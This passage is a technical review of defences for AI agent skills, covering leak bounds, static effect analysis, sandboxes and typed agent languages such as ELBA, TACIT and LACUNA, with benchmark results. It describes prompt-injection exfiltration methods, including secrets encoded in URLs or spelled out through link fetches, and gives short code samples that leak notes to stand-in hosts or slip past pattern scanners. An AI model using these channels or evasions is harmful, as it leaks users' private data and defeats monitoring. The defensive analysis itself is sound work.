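According to Metere's preprint, a refined dispatcher also limits leaks to log₂(|D| + 1) bits per tool call, where |D| is the number of declared capabilities. One bit is the information in the answer to a yes-or-no question when both answers are equally likely.

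The bound comes from the function π, whose result is either a declared capability or a refusal, so there are |D| + 1 possible results. Let S be the secret that the model has read and Y the model's output. An observer who sees only π(Y) learns at most as much about S as π(Y) contains in total, a quantity called its entropy and written H. The entropy of something with k possible values is at most log₂ k, which it reaches when all k are equally likely. So:

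```
information about S in π(Y)  ≤  H(π(Y))  ≤  log₂(|D| + 1)
```

The summariser has two capabilities, so there are three possible results: `net.egress`, `fs.read` and a refusal. The bound is log₂ 3, or about 1.58 bits. Metere also cites the data-processing inequality, a theorem that processing a message cannot add information about its source. The theorem holds for π, but the bound comes only from counting π's possible results.

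The mathematics is correct for an observer who sees only the capability's name, but a web server sees the whole URL. The dispatcher's type accepts a tool call with its arguments, and the dispatcher has to pass those arguments on because `fetch_page` can't work without a URL.

Suppose the URL has room for 100 characters that the model can choose freely from an alphabet of 64 symbols: upper-case and lower-case letters, digits, the hyphen and the underscore. There are 64¹⁰⁰ possible strings, and

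```
log₂(64¹⁰⁰) = 100 × log₂ 64 = 100 × 6 = 600 bits
```

One permitted call can therefore carry 600 bits, nearly 380 times Metere's limit of 1.58 bits. A 128-bit secret key fits into 22 of the characters. If the limit held, sending the key would take at least 81 calls.

The bound does not hold while the arguments are unrestricted, so restricting them is a condition for having any such bound. Metere suggests that an operator could summarise or redact the arguments to go below the bound, which wrongly assumes that it already holds without those restrictions.

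The correct count is of the different calls that an observer can tell apart. If the dispatcher permits N of them, one call leaks at most log₂(N + 1) bits. To keep N small, the runtime can require every combination of operation and arguments to come from a finite list, which it fixes before the model reads anything private:

```
{e : Envelope | caps(e) ⊆ D ∧ (op(e), args(e)) ∈ Allowed}
```

The timing matters because a list the model helped write after reading the notes could contain them. With 50 approved URLs and 10 cached files, N is 60 and the bound is log₂ 61, or about 5.9 bits per call. Over 20 calls the total is almost 119 bits, close to the size of a 128-bit key, so the runtime also has to limit the number of calls. A maximum argument length also gives a bound, but in the example above it is 600 bits.

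A runtime might relax the rule and let the model follow any link on a page it has already fetched. An attacker can then publish a page with 64 links, each standing for a different symbol, and ask the model to spell out the secret by opening the matching links in order. Each fetch reveals about 6 bits, so the 128-bit key takes 22 fetches. This is much slower than sending the key in one long URL, and unusual enough for a monitor to detect.

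These figures don't include the timing of the calls. A server that records when each request arrives can learn something from the delays, and Metere leaves timing and other side channels out of scope. Even a small number of bits can reveal a short secret. For example, a single permitted fetch can answer a yes-or-no question such as whether a company is about to be sold.

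## Side effects inside tools and scripts

The dispatcher tests a tool call before the tool starts. From then on the tool is an ordinary program, and it may do more than its capability label suggests. This function is adapted from an example by Adam, Lu and colleagues (2026), in *Towards Practically-Secure Tools for AI Agents*:

```python
def write_file(path, text):
    requests.post(METRICS_URL, json={"tool": "write_file", "size": len(text)})
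    with open(path, "w") as f:
        f.write(text)
```

The function writes a file and also reports each use to a metrics server. If the map from tools to capabilities lists only the file write, a skill without network permission can still trigger a network request by calling the function.

*Description-Code Inconsistency in Real-world MCP Servers* (2026) compares tools' descriptions with their code and has a category for undeclared side effects, such as a permanent write by a tool whose description implies that it only reads. *Why Static Skill Inconsistencies Do Not Equate to Runtime Risks* (2026) calls a skill "under-promised" if its code has capabilities that its documentation omits. As its title indicates, such a mismatch does not necessarily cause harm when the skill runs.

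### Finding effects without running the script

Metere proposes to analyse the scripts in a skill before the skill loads. Let E(p) be the set of all effects that a script p could have, where an effect is a capability together with its host, path or other argument. The analyser computes a set Ê(p) that is at least as large, and compares it with the manifest:

```
if  E(p) ⊆ Ê(p)  and  Ê(p) ⊆ D,  then  E(p) ⊆ D
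```

The analyser has to overestimate a script's side effects because the exact set isn't computable in general. A script might delete a file only after some long calculation ends, and no program can determine for every calculation whether it will end. Metere's claim that the exact set is computable for mainstream scripting languages is therefore false in general.

The technique is called abstract interpretation. The analyser works through the script using summaries in place of actual values. Take these lines:

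```python
host = "docs" if fast else "archive"
url = "https://" + host + ".example.com/guide.html"
page = requests.get(url)
```

The analyser doesn't know whether `fast` is true, so it follows both branches and summarises the host as `*.example.com`. It then looks up the effect of each library call in a table. In Metere's table for Python, `requests.get(u)` has the effect `net.egress` on any host `u` could refer to, and `open(p, "w")` has the effect `fs.write.irrev` on any path `p` could refer to. For a loop, the analyser re-analyses the body until the set of effects stops growing, making the summaries coarser if necessary so that it finishes in a limited number of rounds.

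The analyser can't summarise the effects of some code. Python's `eval` runs a string as a program, and reflection lets a script choose a function by name while it runs. If a script can reach either, the analyser assigns it "any effect", which is more than any reasonable manifest would declare. It does the same when a script starts another program, unless that program also belongs to the skill and the analyser has read it. An author can remove such code or accept a lower verification level, which Metere thinks is right for skills whose purpose is to run arbitrary code.

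Metere's Theorem 1 states that if Ê(p) stays within D for every script p, no run of any script has an effect outside D. This holds only if every table entry is complete. The entry for `requests.get` is incomplete because the function follows redirects by default. A sound entry would be "any host" unless the script turns redirects off.

### The undeclared cache write

The summariser's script saves each page to the cache, which its manifest doesn't allow. In Metere's worked example, the analysis reports:

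```
Ê(p) = { net.egress(*.example.com),
         fs.read(./.cache/),
         fs.write.rev(./.cache/) }
```

The third effect is missing from D, so the operator has to add it to the manifest or change the script. Metere says catching such omissions is the most common practical benefit of the analysis, since scripts change and their manifests fall behind. This is useful even when there is no attacker.

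The label on the write is probably wrong, though. A script that calls `open` bypasses the runtime's buffer, so the write is irreversible and its effect should be `fs.write.irrev(./.cache/)`, as listed in the Python table. If the operator adds `fs.write.rev` to the manifest, as in the example, an analyser that follows the table will still report an undeclared write. The script could instead return the page and let the runtime write it.

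If the model supplies the URL as an argument, the analyser has no information about its value and must report `net.egress` to any host. It can report the narrower pattern `*.example.com` only if the script checks that the host matches and the analyser can interpret that check.

### What the released analyser does

Metere attributes the worked example to rules for Semgrep, an established code-analysis tool. The analyser in the released framework is much simpler. It searches Python, shell, JavaScript and TypeScript source with regular expressions and assigns "any effect" to scripts that contain `eval`, `exec`, `new Function` or a dynamic import.

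Regular expressions match text, and the same effect can have many spellings. A pattern for `requests.get(` misses both of these:

```python
from requests import get as load
load(url)

getattr(requests, "g" + "et")(url)
```

A broader pattern could flag every import of `requests`, but a script could still make the request through another library. Metere calls the verdict "conservative by construction", but this is true only of the constructs on the list. Theorem 1 assumes a sound analyser, so it does not apply to this scanner. The scanner can still find unintentional omissions such as the cache write, but an attacker can read the public patterns and write code that avoids them.

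An analyser should at least distinguish "no undeclared effects" from "could not tell". *SkillConsist* (2026) compares what a skill declares with what its code does. It reports that an item on one side has no match on the other only if its inventory of the other side is complete. Otherwise it returns "Unknown", and a runtime could withhold the higher verification levels in that case.

### Searching for sessions that the log does not explain

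Metere's remaining method checks the audit log against actual changes, building on a check from the companion paper. The runtime takes a snapshot of chosen files and other objects before a session and compares it with their state afterwards. Every change should match one log record of an approved and executed call, with the same operation and target, and every record should match one change. Metere calls this two-way match the biconditional criterion.

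It detects four faults:

- a change that nobody approved
- a record of a change that never happened
- an approved call that failed silently although the log records a success
- a change to the wrong target

Metere simulated 27,000 sessions, leaving one fifth clean and injecting one of these faults into each of the rest. The check caught every fault and raised no false alarms. This result is largely true by definition, because each injected fault was a mismatch of the kind the check is designed to detect.

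The definition counts only records of irreversible calls. A buffered write that the runtime commits also changes a file but has no such record, so the check would report a fault. This problem did not show up because the simulated agents used only reads and irreversible writes.

The check gives some protection against scripts that were analysed incorrectly. If a script deletes a file in the collection without reporting it to the runtime, the check finds a deletion with no matching record. But it detects the deletion only after the file is gone, and it misses a script that sends data to another server, because that changes nothing in the collection.

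The search is meant to find such failures before the skill loads. It is a form of bounded model checking, in which a solver looks for a violation in any run up to a fixed length K. Metere represents a session as a sequence of up to K tool calls, each with the state of the world after it, and encodes the approval policy as a function that admits or denies each call. The solver then looks for a session with this property:

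```
at some step i, the world changes,
and the log has no admitted call for step i
```

If the formula is satisfiable, the developer gets a concrete sequence of calls that shows the fault. If it is unsatisfiable, no session of up to K calls violates the criterion, at least in the encoding. The search doesn't cover bugs in the runtime's JavaScript unless somebody has encoded that code too.

Metere sets K to the number of calls that the runtime's buffer can hold before the log check runs, typically about 100, so that the check covers any longer sequence of calls. However, Metere's paper on the framework limits the buffer by memory, by default to half the machine's RAM. Thousands of small writes could fit in that, and a fetch doesn't have to enter the buffer at all, so the runtime would need a separate limit on the number of calls.

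The released code doesn't use a solver for this search. It tries every sequence, treating each call as one of the |D| declared capabilities or as "undeclared". There are (|D| + 1)^K sequences of length K. Metere considers this practical for up to ten capabilities and eight calls, but the worked example has three capabilities and 100 calls:

```
ten capabilities,   K = 8:      11^8   ≈ 2.1 × 10^8
three capabilities, K = 100:    4^100  ≈ 1.6 × 10^60
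```

A program that tried a billion sequences per second would need about 5 × 10⁴³ years for the second search. With three capabilities, the same amount of work as the first search covers sessions of only 13 calls. Metere reports that Z3, a widely used SMT solver, handled the worked example in a few seconds. This is plausible because a solver can use the formula to check many sequences at once, but the released enumerator cannot reproduce the result.

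The enumerator also has no separate symbols for individual files or hosts, so it can't represent a session in which the runtime approves a write to one file but changes another. The unit tests Metere lists for it cover unlogged and denied calls, but not calls that act on the wrong file or host.

A proof by induction would probably work better than either search. The developer would show that the log and the world match at the start and that every call preserves the match. A solver can check the second part with one small formula because it concerns a single step, and the result covers sessions of any length. The violation Metere searches for already concerns a single step.

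### The evidence bundle

A skill at the highest verification level comes with four files of evidence:

| File | Contents |
|---|---|
| `static.json` | the effects found in each script, with the analyser's version and rules |
| `types.proof` | the result for the dispatcher |
| `smt.unsat` | the search formula and the solver's certificate that it is unsatisfiable |
| `manifest.attest.json` | a signed statement with the hashes of the manifest and the other three files |

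The model for this is proof-carrying code, which George Necula described in 1997. The producer of a program supplies a proof that it is safe, and the recipient checks the proof rather than trusting the producer. Checking a proof usually takes much less work than finding one. Metere's runtime instead repeats most of the work. When it loads the skill, it verifies the signatures and the signer's authority, analyses the scripts again, checks the dispatcher again, reruns the search and compares the results with the files.

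This detects edited evidence and scripts changed since the signing. It also prevents a dishonest producer from simply inventing a favourable result. But the runtime repeats the analysis with the same patterns, so a script that evaded them on the producer's machine evades them again. In the released code, the hash that identifies the search covers only D and K, so two skills with the same manifest entries and the same K have the same hash even if their scripts have nothing in common.

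The preprint is inconsistent about what happens if a re-check fails. In its description of the procedure, the runtime lowers the skill two levels, from "formal" to "declared". Elsewhere, it refuses to load the skill. Under the rules in Metere's companion paper, a "declared" skill can still make its declared irreversible calls without a human's approval, and the runtime no longer runs the log check between rounds. Somebody who tampers with the bundle would therefore face less checking than somebody who leaves it alone. Refusing to load the skill is safer, and the released verifier appears to do this.

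Metere reports that the package's 53 unit tests raised the framework's total from 208 to 261. They also cover pattern matches, log violations, signatures, edited evidence and changed scripts. The tests help show that the parts behave as designed in those cases, but Metere gives no figure for how many effects the patterns miss in real skills.

### What the composition theorem proves

Metere's Theorem 4 combines the methods. It has four assumptions:

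1. The analysis has found that every script's effects stay within D.
2. The dispatcher type-checks with its refined input.
3. The search has found no violation.
4. The runtime performs the log check whenever it empties its buffer.

The conclusion is that the skill has capability containment in every session.

The theorem is false as stated, because containment also counts refused calls. The summariser's refused `pay` call is a counterexample even if all four assumptions hold. The error in the proof sketch is the step from "no undeclared call reaches a host API" to "the model's part of the trace contains only declared capabilities".

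The definition is also too weak because it compares only the names of capabilities and ignores their arguments. A script that contacts `attacker.test` adds `net.egress` to the trace. The summariser has declared `net.egress`, so the session still counts as contained.

Both problems disappear if the property refers to effects that actually occur and includes their arguments:

```
for every session and every effect (c, v) that occurs in it:
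  some entry in D covers capability c with argument v
```

The proof is then short. If the runtime carries out an approved call, the dispatcher's test has already found an entry that covers it. If one of the skill's scripts causes the effect, the analysis has found such an entry. Neither step uses the search or the log check, so containment doesn't require assumptions 3 and 4. Those assumptions concern the log's accuracy, a separate property that matters for investigating incidents. Metere also argues that containment implies an accurate log, but that argument assumes that the log correctly records every executed effect, which is most of what it is meant to prove.

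The restated theorem still needs the four premises of the dispatcher's guarantee, including a correct map from tools to capabilities. The scripts add three more:

- **The analyser is sound**, including its table of library functions.
- **The code that runs is the code that the analyser read.** The signature covers the skill's own files. A script that imports `requests` runs whichever version is on the machine, and an update can change its effects without changing the skill.
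- **The analyser has read every program that a call can start.** Tools that belong to the runtime or to a remote server are not part of the skill, and neither are commands that the model writes during the session.

The last premise often fails for agents that can use a shell. In *Scan the Skill, Govern the Action* (Taneja and Weber, 2026), an agent followed the documentation of 39 real skills in a sandbox and ran 144 commands, only two of which appeared word for word in the documentation. For 50 commands (34.7%), no code block in the skill's documentation contained a command with the same class of consequence. The sample is small and includes only one agent, and Taneja and Weber work for a company that develops a gate for such commands. Still, the result suggests that reading a skill beforehand doesn't fully show what an agent will run.

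A sandbox can restrict programs that no analyser has read. *Sandlock* (Wang and Zheng, 2026) describes one for Linux that needs no administrator privileges. The kernel enforces the rules that don't depend on run-time values, and a small supervisor program handles the decisions that do. Metere objects that sandboxes cannot check whether an operation matches the manifest the operator approved, but a runtime could generate the sandbox's rules from that manifest. For the summariser, the rules would allow reads from the cache directory and connections to hosts under example.com. The undeclared cache write would then fail, however the script was written.

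### Checking that tools use their sandboxes

Adam and colleagues at Brown University apply sandboxes and code analysis together to tool servers. They assume that a tool's developer may be careless or may describe the tool misleadingly, and that an attacker may control the model through prompt injection.

The analyser first summarises the kinds of effect each tool can have in a synopsis. For the `write_file` tool with hidden metrics, the synopsis lists a file write and a network write. The server sends the synopsis to the client when they connect. Before every tool call, a policy engine on the client compares the synopsis with the user's policy, which might allow file writes in the workspace but forbid network writes while the agent handles private code.

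A synopsis cannot guarantee that a write will stay in the workspace, because the path isn't known until the call. The developer therefore replaces the ordinary write with a sandboxed version, which takes the client's restrictions as an extra argument and tests the actual path against them. A second analysis checks that the tool has no effects outside such sandboxed operations and that no code alters the restrictions before they reach those operations. If an effect has no sandbox, the policy engine rejects the call unless the policy explicitly allows that effect.

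The refined dispatcher divides the work between a run-time test and a static check in the same way, and this division would also suit the summariser's script. The script could fetch pages through a function that tests every host, including any reached by redirect. The analyser would then only have to confirm that the script uses this function.

Adam and colleagues built a prototype for tool servers written in Rust and tested it on an existing server for programming tools. Each of their three scenarios has an intended variant and a harmful one:

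- An agent saves an API key in a project's settings file and adds a line to the user's shell configuration. In the harmful variant, it guesses the wrong directory for the settings file.
- A developer uses one server for both open-source and proprietary code. In the harmful variant, the server sends undisclosed usage metrics over the network.
- An agent copies a settings file into a project and later publishes the project on GitHub. In the harmful variant, the file contains a secret key.

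Sessions with two Claude Haiku models were recorded and replayed under four arrangements, so that differences in the models' output could not affect the comparison.

| Protection | Intended variants allowed | Harmful variants blocked |
|---|---|---|
| None | 3 of 3 | 0 of 3 |
| One sandbox around the whole server | 2 of 3 | 1 of 3 |
| Code analysis alone | 2 of 3 | 3 of 3 |
| Code analysis with sandboxes in each tool | 3 of 3 | 3 of 3 |

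The single sandbox had one fixed policy, which blocked the legitimate change to the shell configuration because such changes are usually suspicious, but let both network leaks through. Code analysis alone blocked all file writes in the first scenario because it couldn't determine where they would go. A regular expression or even a sound analyser would have the same problem with the summariser, because it couldn't determine which URL the model would supply.

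The experiment covers only six cases, all designed by the researchers. An "oracle" gave the prototype the right policy for each request, standing in for a person or model that would have to write it. In the GitHub scenario, the agent had been told whether the file contained a secret. The results show that the mechanism can enforce a suitable policy, but not that an agent will usually have one.

Rust also makes the analysis easier than Python or JavaScript would, and Adam and colleagues expect more false rejections in those languages. Their analyser cannot follow effects into databases, web services or shell commands. The prototype runs shell commands in a temporary file system and checks the changes at the end. It sends network requests through a proxy that allows only certain domains. The proxy doesn't distinguish between addresses within a domain, so it cannot let the agent read a social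 media post without also letting it publish one.

For a remote server, the client also needs evidence that the server is running the program the analyser read. Adam and colleagues propose remote attestation, in which security hardware on the server certifies which program is running. They leave attacks on the server's machine and operating system out of scope.

### The trusted base

Each method moves some trust from the skill's author to another component. If one of these components is wrong, the guarantee can fail without any visible error:

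| Component | Possible failure |
|---|---|
| Analyser | overlooks an effect in a script |
| Type checker | accepts code that dispatches an untested call |
| Solver | reports that no counterexample exists when there is one |
| Runtime | carries out a call without consulting the dispatcher |
| Signer | approves a manifest that is too broad |

Metere proposes naming the trusted components, auditing them once and reusing the audit. The bundle records the tool versions, so an operator can tell which audit applies. The analyser needs a new audit whenever the libraries change, because its table of library functions has to change with them.

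The released version replaces the type checker with a probe and the solver with an enumerator. Metere says a person can audit this default stack in an afternoon, which nobody could do for Semgrep and Z3. A small trusted base is worth having, but anyone who audited this one would find that the script scanner is unsound. For the theorem to apply, an operator needs a real analyser and has to trust a larger program.

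Metere assumes that the runtime is correct and suggests adding a verified runtime later. The threat model in Metere's companion paper also excludes attackers who have the signing key, have altered the runtime's program file or can access the stored log. An attacker with the key could sign a malicious skill whose manifest lists everything it does, and its scripts would pass even a perfect analyser. An honest signer who approves an unnecessary `pay` entry creates a similar weakness.

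## Type-checking the programs a model writes

In the designs described so far, the model sends one tool call at a time, and a type checker can analyze only the software that receives it. In three systems from 2026, the model instead writes a short program in a typed language, which the runtime compiles and runs only if it type-checks. A checker can therefore analyze the caller's source code before it runs, as Vazou, Bakst and Jhala's checker did with Haskell code that used capabilities.

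These systems rely on effect types, which record the side effects a computation may have, on abstract types with hidden constructors, like `Approved` in the `Gate` module, and on object capabilities that the compiler tracks in the types of other values. They hardly use refinement types, and they mostly leave conditions on particular hosts, paths and amounts to run-time checks. Refinement types could let the compiler do some of those checks.

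### What a checker can do with a whole program

Suppose the summariser may also read a file of private notes. A hostile page asks the model to read the file and put its text into a web address. As separate tool calls, both steps pass the refined dispatcher, because the skill has permission to read the file and to contact the host. As a program, they look like this:

```scala
val notes = readNotes()
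fetchPage("https://community.example.com/p?q=" + notes)
```

The checker detects that the second line uses the result of the first. If the type of `notes` rules out this use, the compiler rejects the program before the file is read.

*LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026) gives an example of why it helps to reject a program as a whole. An agent has to subtract 50 from a balance of 100 and return the new balance as an integer. The model writes one line that subtracts 50 and another that returns a sentence. In Python, the subtraction would take effect before the mistake showed up. The paper's system, also called LACUNA, rejects both lines, so the balance stays at 100. It then sends the model the compiler's error message (a string where an integer should be), and the model tries again.

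Type-checking protects only against errors that a compiler can find. If a program type-checks but a server fails to respond at the third line, the first two lines have already run. The model also often needs to see a result before it can choose the next step, so it submits several programs in a session, and the checker has to check each one before the later ones are written.

### Restricting an agent by its result type

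Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova (2026), in *Language-Based Agent Control*, embed the agent in Haskell. Their library, ELBA, has one main function:

```haskell
agent :: Defs -> Prompt -> t
```

`Defs` lists the functions and types the model's code may use, and `t` is the type of result the surrounding program expects. When the program reaches this call, ELBA prompts the model for a Haskell expression of type `t` and checks it. ELBA runs the expression if it passes and otherwise returns the error to the model for another attempt.

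In Haskell, the result type also limits side effects. Functions that read files or contact servers have the effect type `IO`, and any expression that runs one of them has that type too. If the program expects a plain `Int`, the model's code can do arithmetic but cannot delete a file. Haskell has official ways around this rule, such as `unsafePerformIO`, so the model's code must use Safe Haskell, a restricted version of the language that excludes them.

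Most agents need some side effects, so the developer defines a narrower effect type. In Zhou and colleagues' main example, an agent compiles a bibliography, and every entry must come from DBLP, a database of computer science publications. In outline, the library looks like this:

```haskell
dblpSearch      :: String -> BibIO [DOI]
dblpFetchBib    :: DOI -> BibIO (Trusted Bib)
appendToBibFile :: Trusted Bib -> BibIO ()
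```

The library hides the constructor of `Trusted`, so the model's code can get a `Trusted Bib` only by fetching it from DBLP. The whole program must have type `BibIO ()`, where `()` means it returns no value. Haskell's ordinary `writeFile` returns an `IO` action instead, so a program that uses it to write an invented entry doesn't type-check. The model can still sort and filter the entries with arbitrary code. This rule needs no refinement type because it concerns only where an entry came from.

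In a test with 100 topics, none of the 925 citations from the ELBA agent had the wrong authors, year or identifier, compared with 19 of 1,002 from an ordinary agent with web search. Both used Claude Sonnet 5. The ordinary agent wrote its citations from search results and memory, so the comparison doesn't isolate the effect of the types. As Zhou and colleagues point out, a single tool that fetches an entry and writes it to the file would also prevent invented entries. But the model would have to inspect the entries one by one instead of sorting them in code. Neither approach ensures that a genuine entry is relevant.

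### Sub-agents and the soundness theorem

ELBA's `agent` function produces one program and has no loop. To continue after seeing a result, the model's code calls `agent` again and includes the result in the new prompt. Haskell infers the expected type of the inner call from its position, so a call inside a `BibIO` program also has type `BibIO`, and the sub-agent can use only the same three operations. The parent can impose a stricter type, such as one without side effects, but it can't use `IO`, for the same reason that it can't call `writeFile`. An injected instruction therefore can't gain permissions by starting a sub-agent.

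Zhou and colleagues prove that any property the host language enforces for well-typed programs also holds for programs with agent calls. They describe a program's behaviour by its traces, where a trace is the sequence of tool calls with observable effects in one run. The proof has three steps:

1. Take a well-typed program that contains agent calls.
2. Replace each agent call with an ordinary function that asks the model for code, type-checks the reply and evaluates it. The reply may contain more agent calls, so this step uses induction on a fixed limit to how deeply they can nest.
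3. The new program has the same type and the same traces but no agent calls, so the host language's guarantee applies to it.

The model can be any function from prompts to programs, including one an attacker has chosen. Zhou and colleagues leave random sampling out of the proof. They say sampling doesn't affect the properties they study, and that a developer can cache the model's replies if a property does require determinism.

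The traces contain only tool calls. An agent call of type `Int` still sends its prompt to the model's provider, so the theorem doesn't cover private text that the surrounding program puts into a prompt.

The theorem also assumes the host language's guarantees, some of which depend on run-time checks. ELBA's file library, for example, represents permission to use a directory as a `Path` value that the model's code can't forge. `readRIO "/etc/passwd"` fails to compile because the argument is a string rather than a `Path`. But when the code adds a file name to a valid `Path`, the library has to follow any symbolic links and check at run time that the result is still inside the directory.

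### ELBA and CaMeL on the Slack tasks

Zhou and colleagues compare ELBA with CaMeL, a system that Edoardo Debenedetti and colleagues described in 2025. In CaMeL, one model writes a program in a subset of Python before it sees any outside data. A second model, which has no tools, extracts values from untrusted text. A custom interpreter runs the program, tracks where each value came from, and blocks uses that a policy forbids. An instruction on a hostile page can't change the program, because the model writes the program before CaMeL reads the page.

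ELBA's agents can read data and then write more code. To make this safe, ELBA uses LIO, an existing Haskell library that labels data by source and confidentiality. After an agent reads an untrusted page, LIO lowers the agent's privileges to those of the page's source. LIO enforces this at run time, and the effect type ensures only that the model's code goes through LIO.

The test used AgentDojo's Slack suite, which has 21 user tasks and 5 injected tasks, or 105 pairs. This is how many of the 105 user tasks each system completed under the benchmark's direct attack:

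| Model | ELBA | CaMeL | ELBA, no policies | CaMeL, no policies |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 52 | 24 | 88 | 69 |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 49 | 30 | 93 | 78 |
| GPT 5.4 | 51 | 23 | 84 | 82 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 43 | 25 | 78 | 56 |

With policies on, ELBA completed about twice as many tasks as CaMeL. Two other wordings of the attack gave similar results. Without policies, the gap was much smaller, and CaMeL did slightly better with GPT 5.4 under both of the other wordings. ELBA took about three times as long, mainly because it calls the model again after reading data.

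Both systems complete fewer tasks when the policies are on. Without an attack, ELBA with Opus 4.7 completed 18 of the 21 tasks with policies off and 10 with them on.

This test couldn't show whether the policies improve security, because every model resisted all 105 attacks even without them. Zhou and colleagues therefore simulated a worst case. Whenever a sub-agent received the attacker's text, ELBA replaced the whole prompt with that text, so that the sub-agent had no other instructions. Without policies, between 16% and 42% of injections succeeded, depending on the model. With policies, none succeeded in 2,940 runs. (The benchmark counted 29 runs as successful attacks because the agent had opened a certain web page. Zhou and colleagues reviewed all 29 and found that no data had leaked.)

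### Capabilities in types

*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) describes TACIT, which checks programs written in Scala 3. TACIT is a Model Context Protocol server, so existing agents such as Claude Code can use it without changes. The model sends Scala code as the argument of a tool call, and TACIT compiles it.

TACIT uses object capabilities. To contact a server, code needs a `Network` object, and to read a file it needs a `FileSystem` object. An experimental feature of Scala called capture checking records which capabilities a value can use in the value's type. This list is the capture set. If `f` is a file, then a function that writes a string to `f` has this type:

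```scala
String ->{f} Unit
```

The capture set is inside the braces. A function of type `String -> Unit` has an empty capture set and is called pure. It can't write to a file, send a request or print anything.

Capture sets also limit how long a permission lasts. `requestFileSystem("/data")` gives a block of code access to one directory until the block ends. If the model's code tries to return a function that would read a file after that, the compiler rejects the program, because the function's type would have to refer to a capability that doesn't exist outside the block.

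Private files arrive in a wrapper, as values of type `Classified[String]`. The main way for the model's code to work with the content is a method called `map`:

```scala
def map[U](op: T -> U): Classified[U]
```

The function `op` has to be pure, and its result stays in the wrapper. If `notes` is a wrapped value, this attempt to leak it doesn't compile, because the function uses the network:

```scala
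notes.map(n => httpGet("https://community.example.com/p?q=" + n))
```

The earlier two-line program would probably compile, since Scala lets code join any value to a string. But the server would receive only `Classified(****)`, the text the wrapper produces whenever code converts it to a string.

The content never reaches the model that writes the code either. If its program prints a wrapped value, the model gets the asterisks and the user sees the real text on a separate channel. To summarise a private document, the program can pass it to a second, trusted model on the user's machine, which returns a wrapped summary. TACIT's design has to assume that this second model keeps no memory of what it reads.

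The wrapper protects only data that arrives inside it, so it doesn't help with notes that the user pastes into the conversation.

Ordinary Scala has casts and reflection, which code could use to remove a capability from a type. TACIT therefore compiles the model's code in *safe mode*, which forbids these features and allows calls only to safe libraries. A library's developer can mark code as safe without the compiler verifying it, and each such mark adds to the trusted base. The type system behind capture checking has machine-checked soundness proofs, but Odersky and colleagues say safe mode still needs a soundness argument of its own.

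The library, rather than the compiler, checks particular paths and hosts. It throws an exception at run time if the code opens a file outside the requested directory or contacts a host that isn't on the requested list. The model's code supplies both the directory and the list, so the types don't stop it from requesting `attacker.test`. A runtime with signed manifests would have to compare each request with D, the declared set.

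### Testing the wrapper

To test TACIT, Odersky and colleagues gave agents a software project with a directory of API keys, a database and confidential documents. They paired each of 12 ordinary tasks with each of 10 prompt injections. Some injections were disguised as system instructions, and others contained ready-made Scala code for reading the secrets. Another 11 tasks came from a malicious user, who asked for the secrets directly or pretended to be, for example, an administrator in an emergency. They ran the resulting 131 trials twice for each model, once with the secrets in the wrapper and once with them as plain strings.

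| | Claude Sonnet 4.6 | MiniMax M2.5 |
|---|---|---|
| No leak, secrets wrapped | 100% | 100% |
| No leak, plain strings | 98.5% | 91.6% |
| Tasks completed, secrets wrapped | 99.2% | 90.0% |
| Tasks completed, plain strings | 83.3% | 88.3% |

A trial counted as a leak if any secret appeared in the agent's output. With the wrapper, only a bug in TACIT could cause a leak, so the 100% result tests the implementation and doesn't measure how often models misbehave. Without the wrapper, Sonnet resisted all 120 injections but gave secrets to the malicious user in 2 of 11 tasks, while MiniMax leaked secrets in three of the injection trials and in 8 of the 11 malicious tasks.

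Sonnet completed more tasks with the wrapper than without it. Odersky and colleagues suggest that this is partly an artifact of the test, because without the wrapper Sonnet often ran out of turns or time. It also sometimes stopped to warn the user when it detected an injection, instead of finishing the task.

### Filling holes in a running program

LACUNA comes from the same group at EPFL in Lausanne and also uses Scala. Its main function resembles ELBA's:

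```scala
def agent[T](task: String): T
```

Programmers call a placeholder like this a *typed hole*, because the type of the missing code is known. When the program reaches the hole, the model receives the task, the expected type, the surrounding source code and a list of the variables in scope. The compiler then checks the model's code as though a programmer had written it there. That code can contain further holes, and when the program reaches those, the model also receives the variables and comments from its earlier code.

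The variables in scope act as the agent's permissions. If the surrounding code has a file capability but no network capability, the model can read the file but can't send it over the network. A developer can grant a permission for one stage of a task and withhold it in the next. But capture checking is optional in LACUNA, and without it the compiler checks the form of the result, not the permissions. Zhao and colleagues also recommend safe mode, since code could otherwise use reflection or start an external program without holding any capability.

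LACUNA can also make TACIT's wrapper more flexible. In TACIT, the model has to write the function for `map` without seeing the private content. LACUNA lets that function contain a hole, which a trusted local model fills with suitable code after reading the content. The compiler still requires this code to be pure.

Both groups at EPFL ran AgentDojo's four suites with the two models from CaMeL's own evaluation, and took CaMeL's figures from its paper. The percentages are user tasks completed:

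| Model | System | Banking | Workspace | Slack | Travel | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | CaMeL | 52.8% | 53.8% | 48.6% | 1.4% | 0 |
| | TACIT | 56.9% | 50.5% | 40.0% | 64.3% | 0 |
| | LACUNA | 63.2% | 56.3% | 42.9% | 63.6% | 7 |
| o4-mini-high | CaMeL | 62.5% | 81.4% | 68.6% | 74.3% | 1 |
| | TACIT | 59.0% | 52.9% | 47.6% | 68.6% | 1 |
| | LACUNA | 66.0% | 55.5% | 49.5% | 71.4% | 1 |

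Each row covers more than 900 attacks, so all three systems stopped nearly all of them. Odersky and colleagues call TACIT's completion rates comparable to CaMeL's, but with o4-mini-high TACIT was behind in all four suites, and by more than 28 percentage points in workspace tasks.

The one successful attack on TACIT occurred during a hotel-booking task. The user asked for hotel A, and the attacker had planted a recommendation for hotel B in hotel A's reviews. The agent booked hotel A but quoted the reviews to the user, and the benchmark counted the mention of hotel B as a success for the attacker. The agent broke no rule, since anyone may read hotel reviews. However, a user could still act on a planted recommendation, and the types do not prevent that.

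The AgentDojo test may also be weaker evidence about pure functions than the test with the secret files. Odersky and colleagues warn in their instructions to the agent that any side effects inside a function passed to `map` happen immediately, and the payment function's signature includes no capability. This version of TACIT therefore seems to have allowed payments inside functions that are supposed to be pure. If so, the protection came mostly from keeping untrusted text away from the model that writes the code.

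Zhao and colleagues acknowledge that LACUNA's compiler can't stop an attacker from persuading the model to misuse a permission that the task needs. The eight attacks that succeeded against LACUNA are consistent with this limitation. The refined dispatcher has the same weakness.

### Can models write this code?

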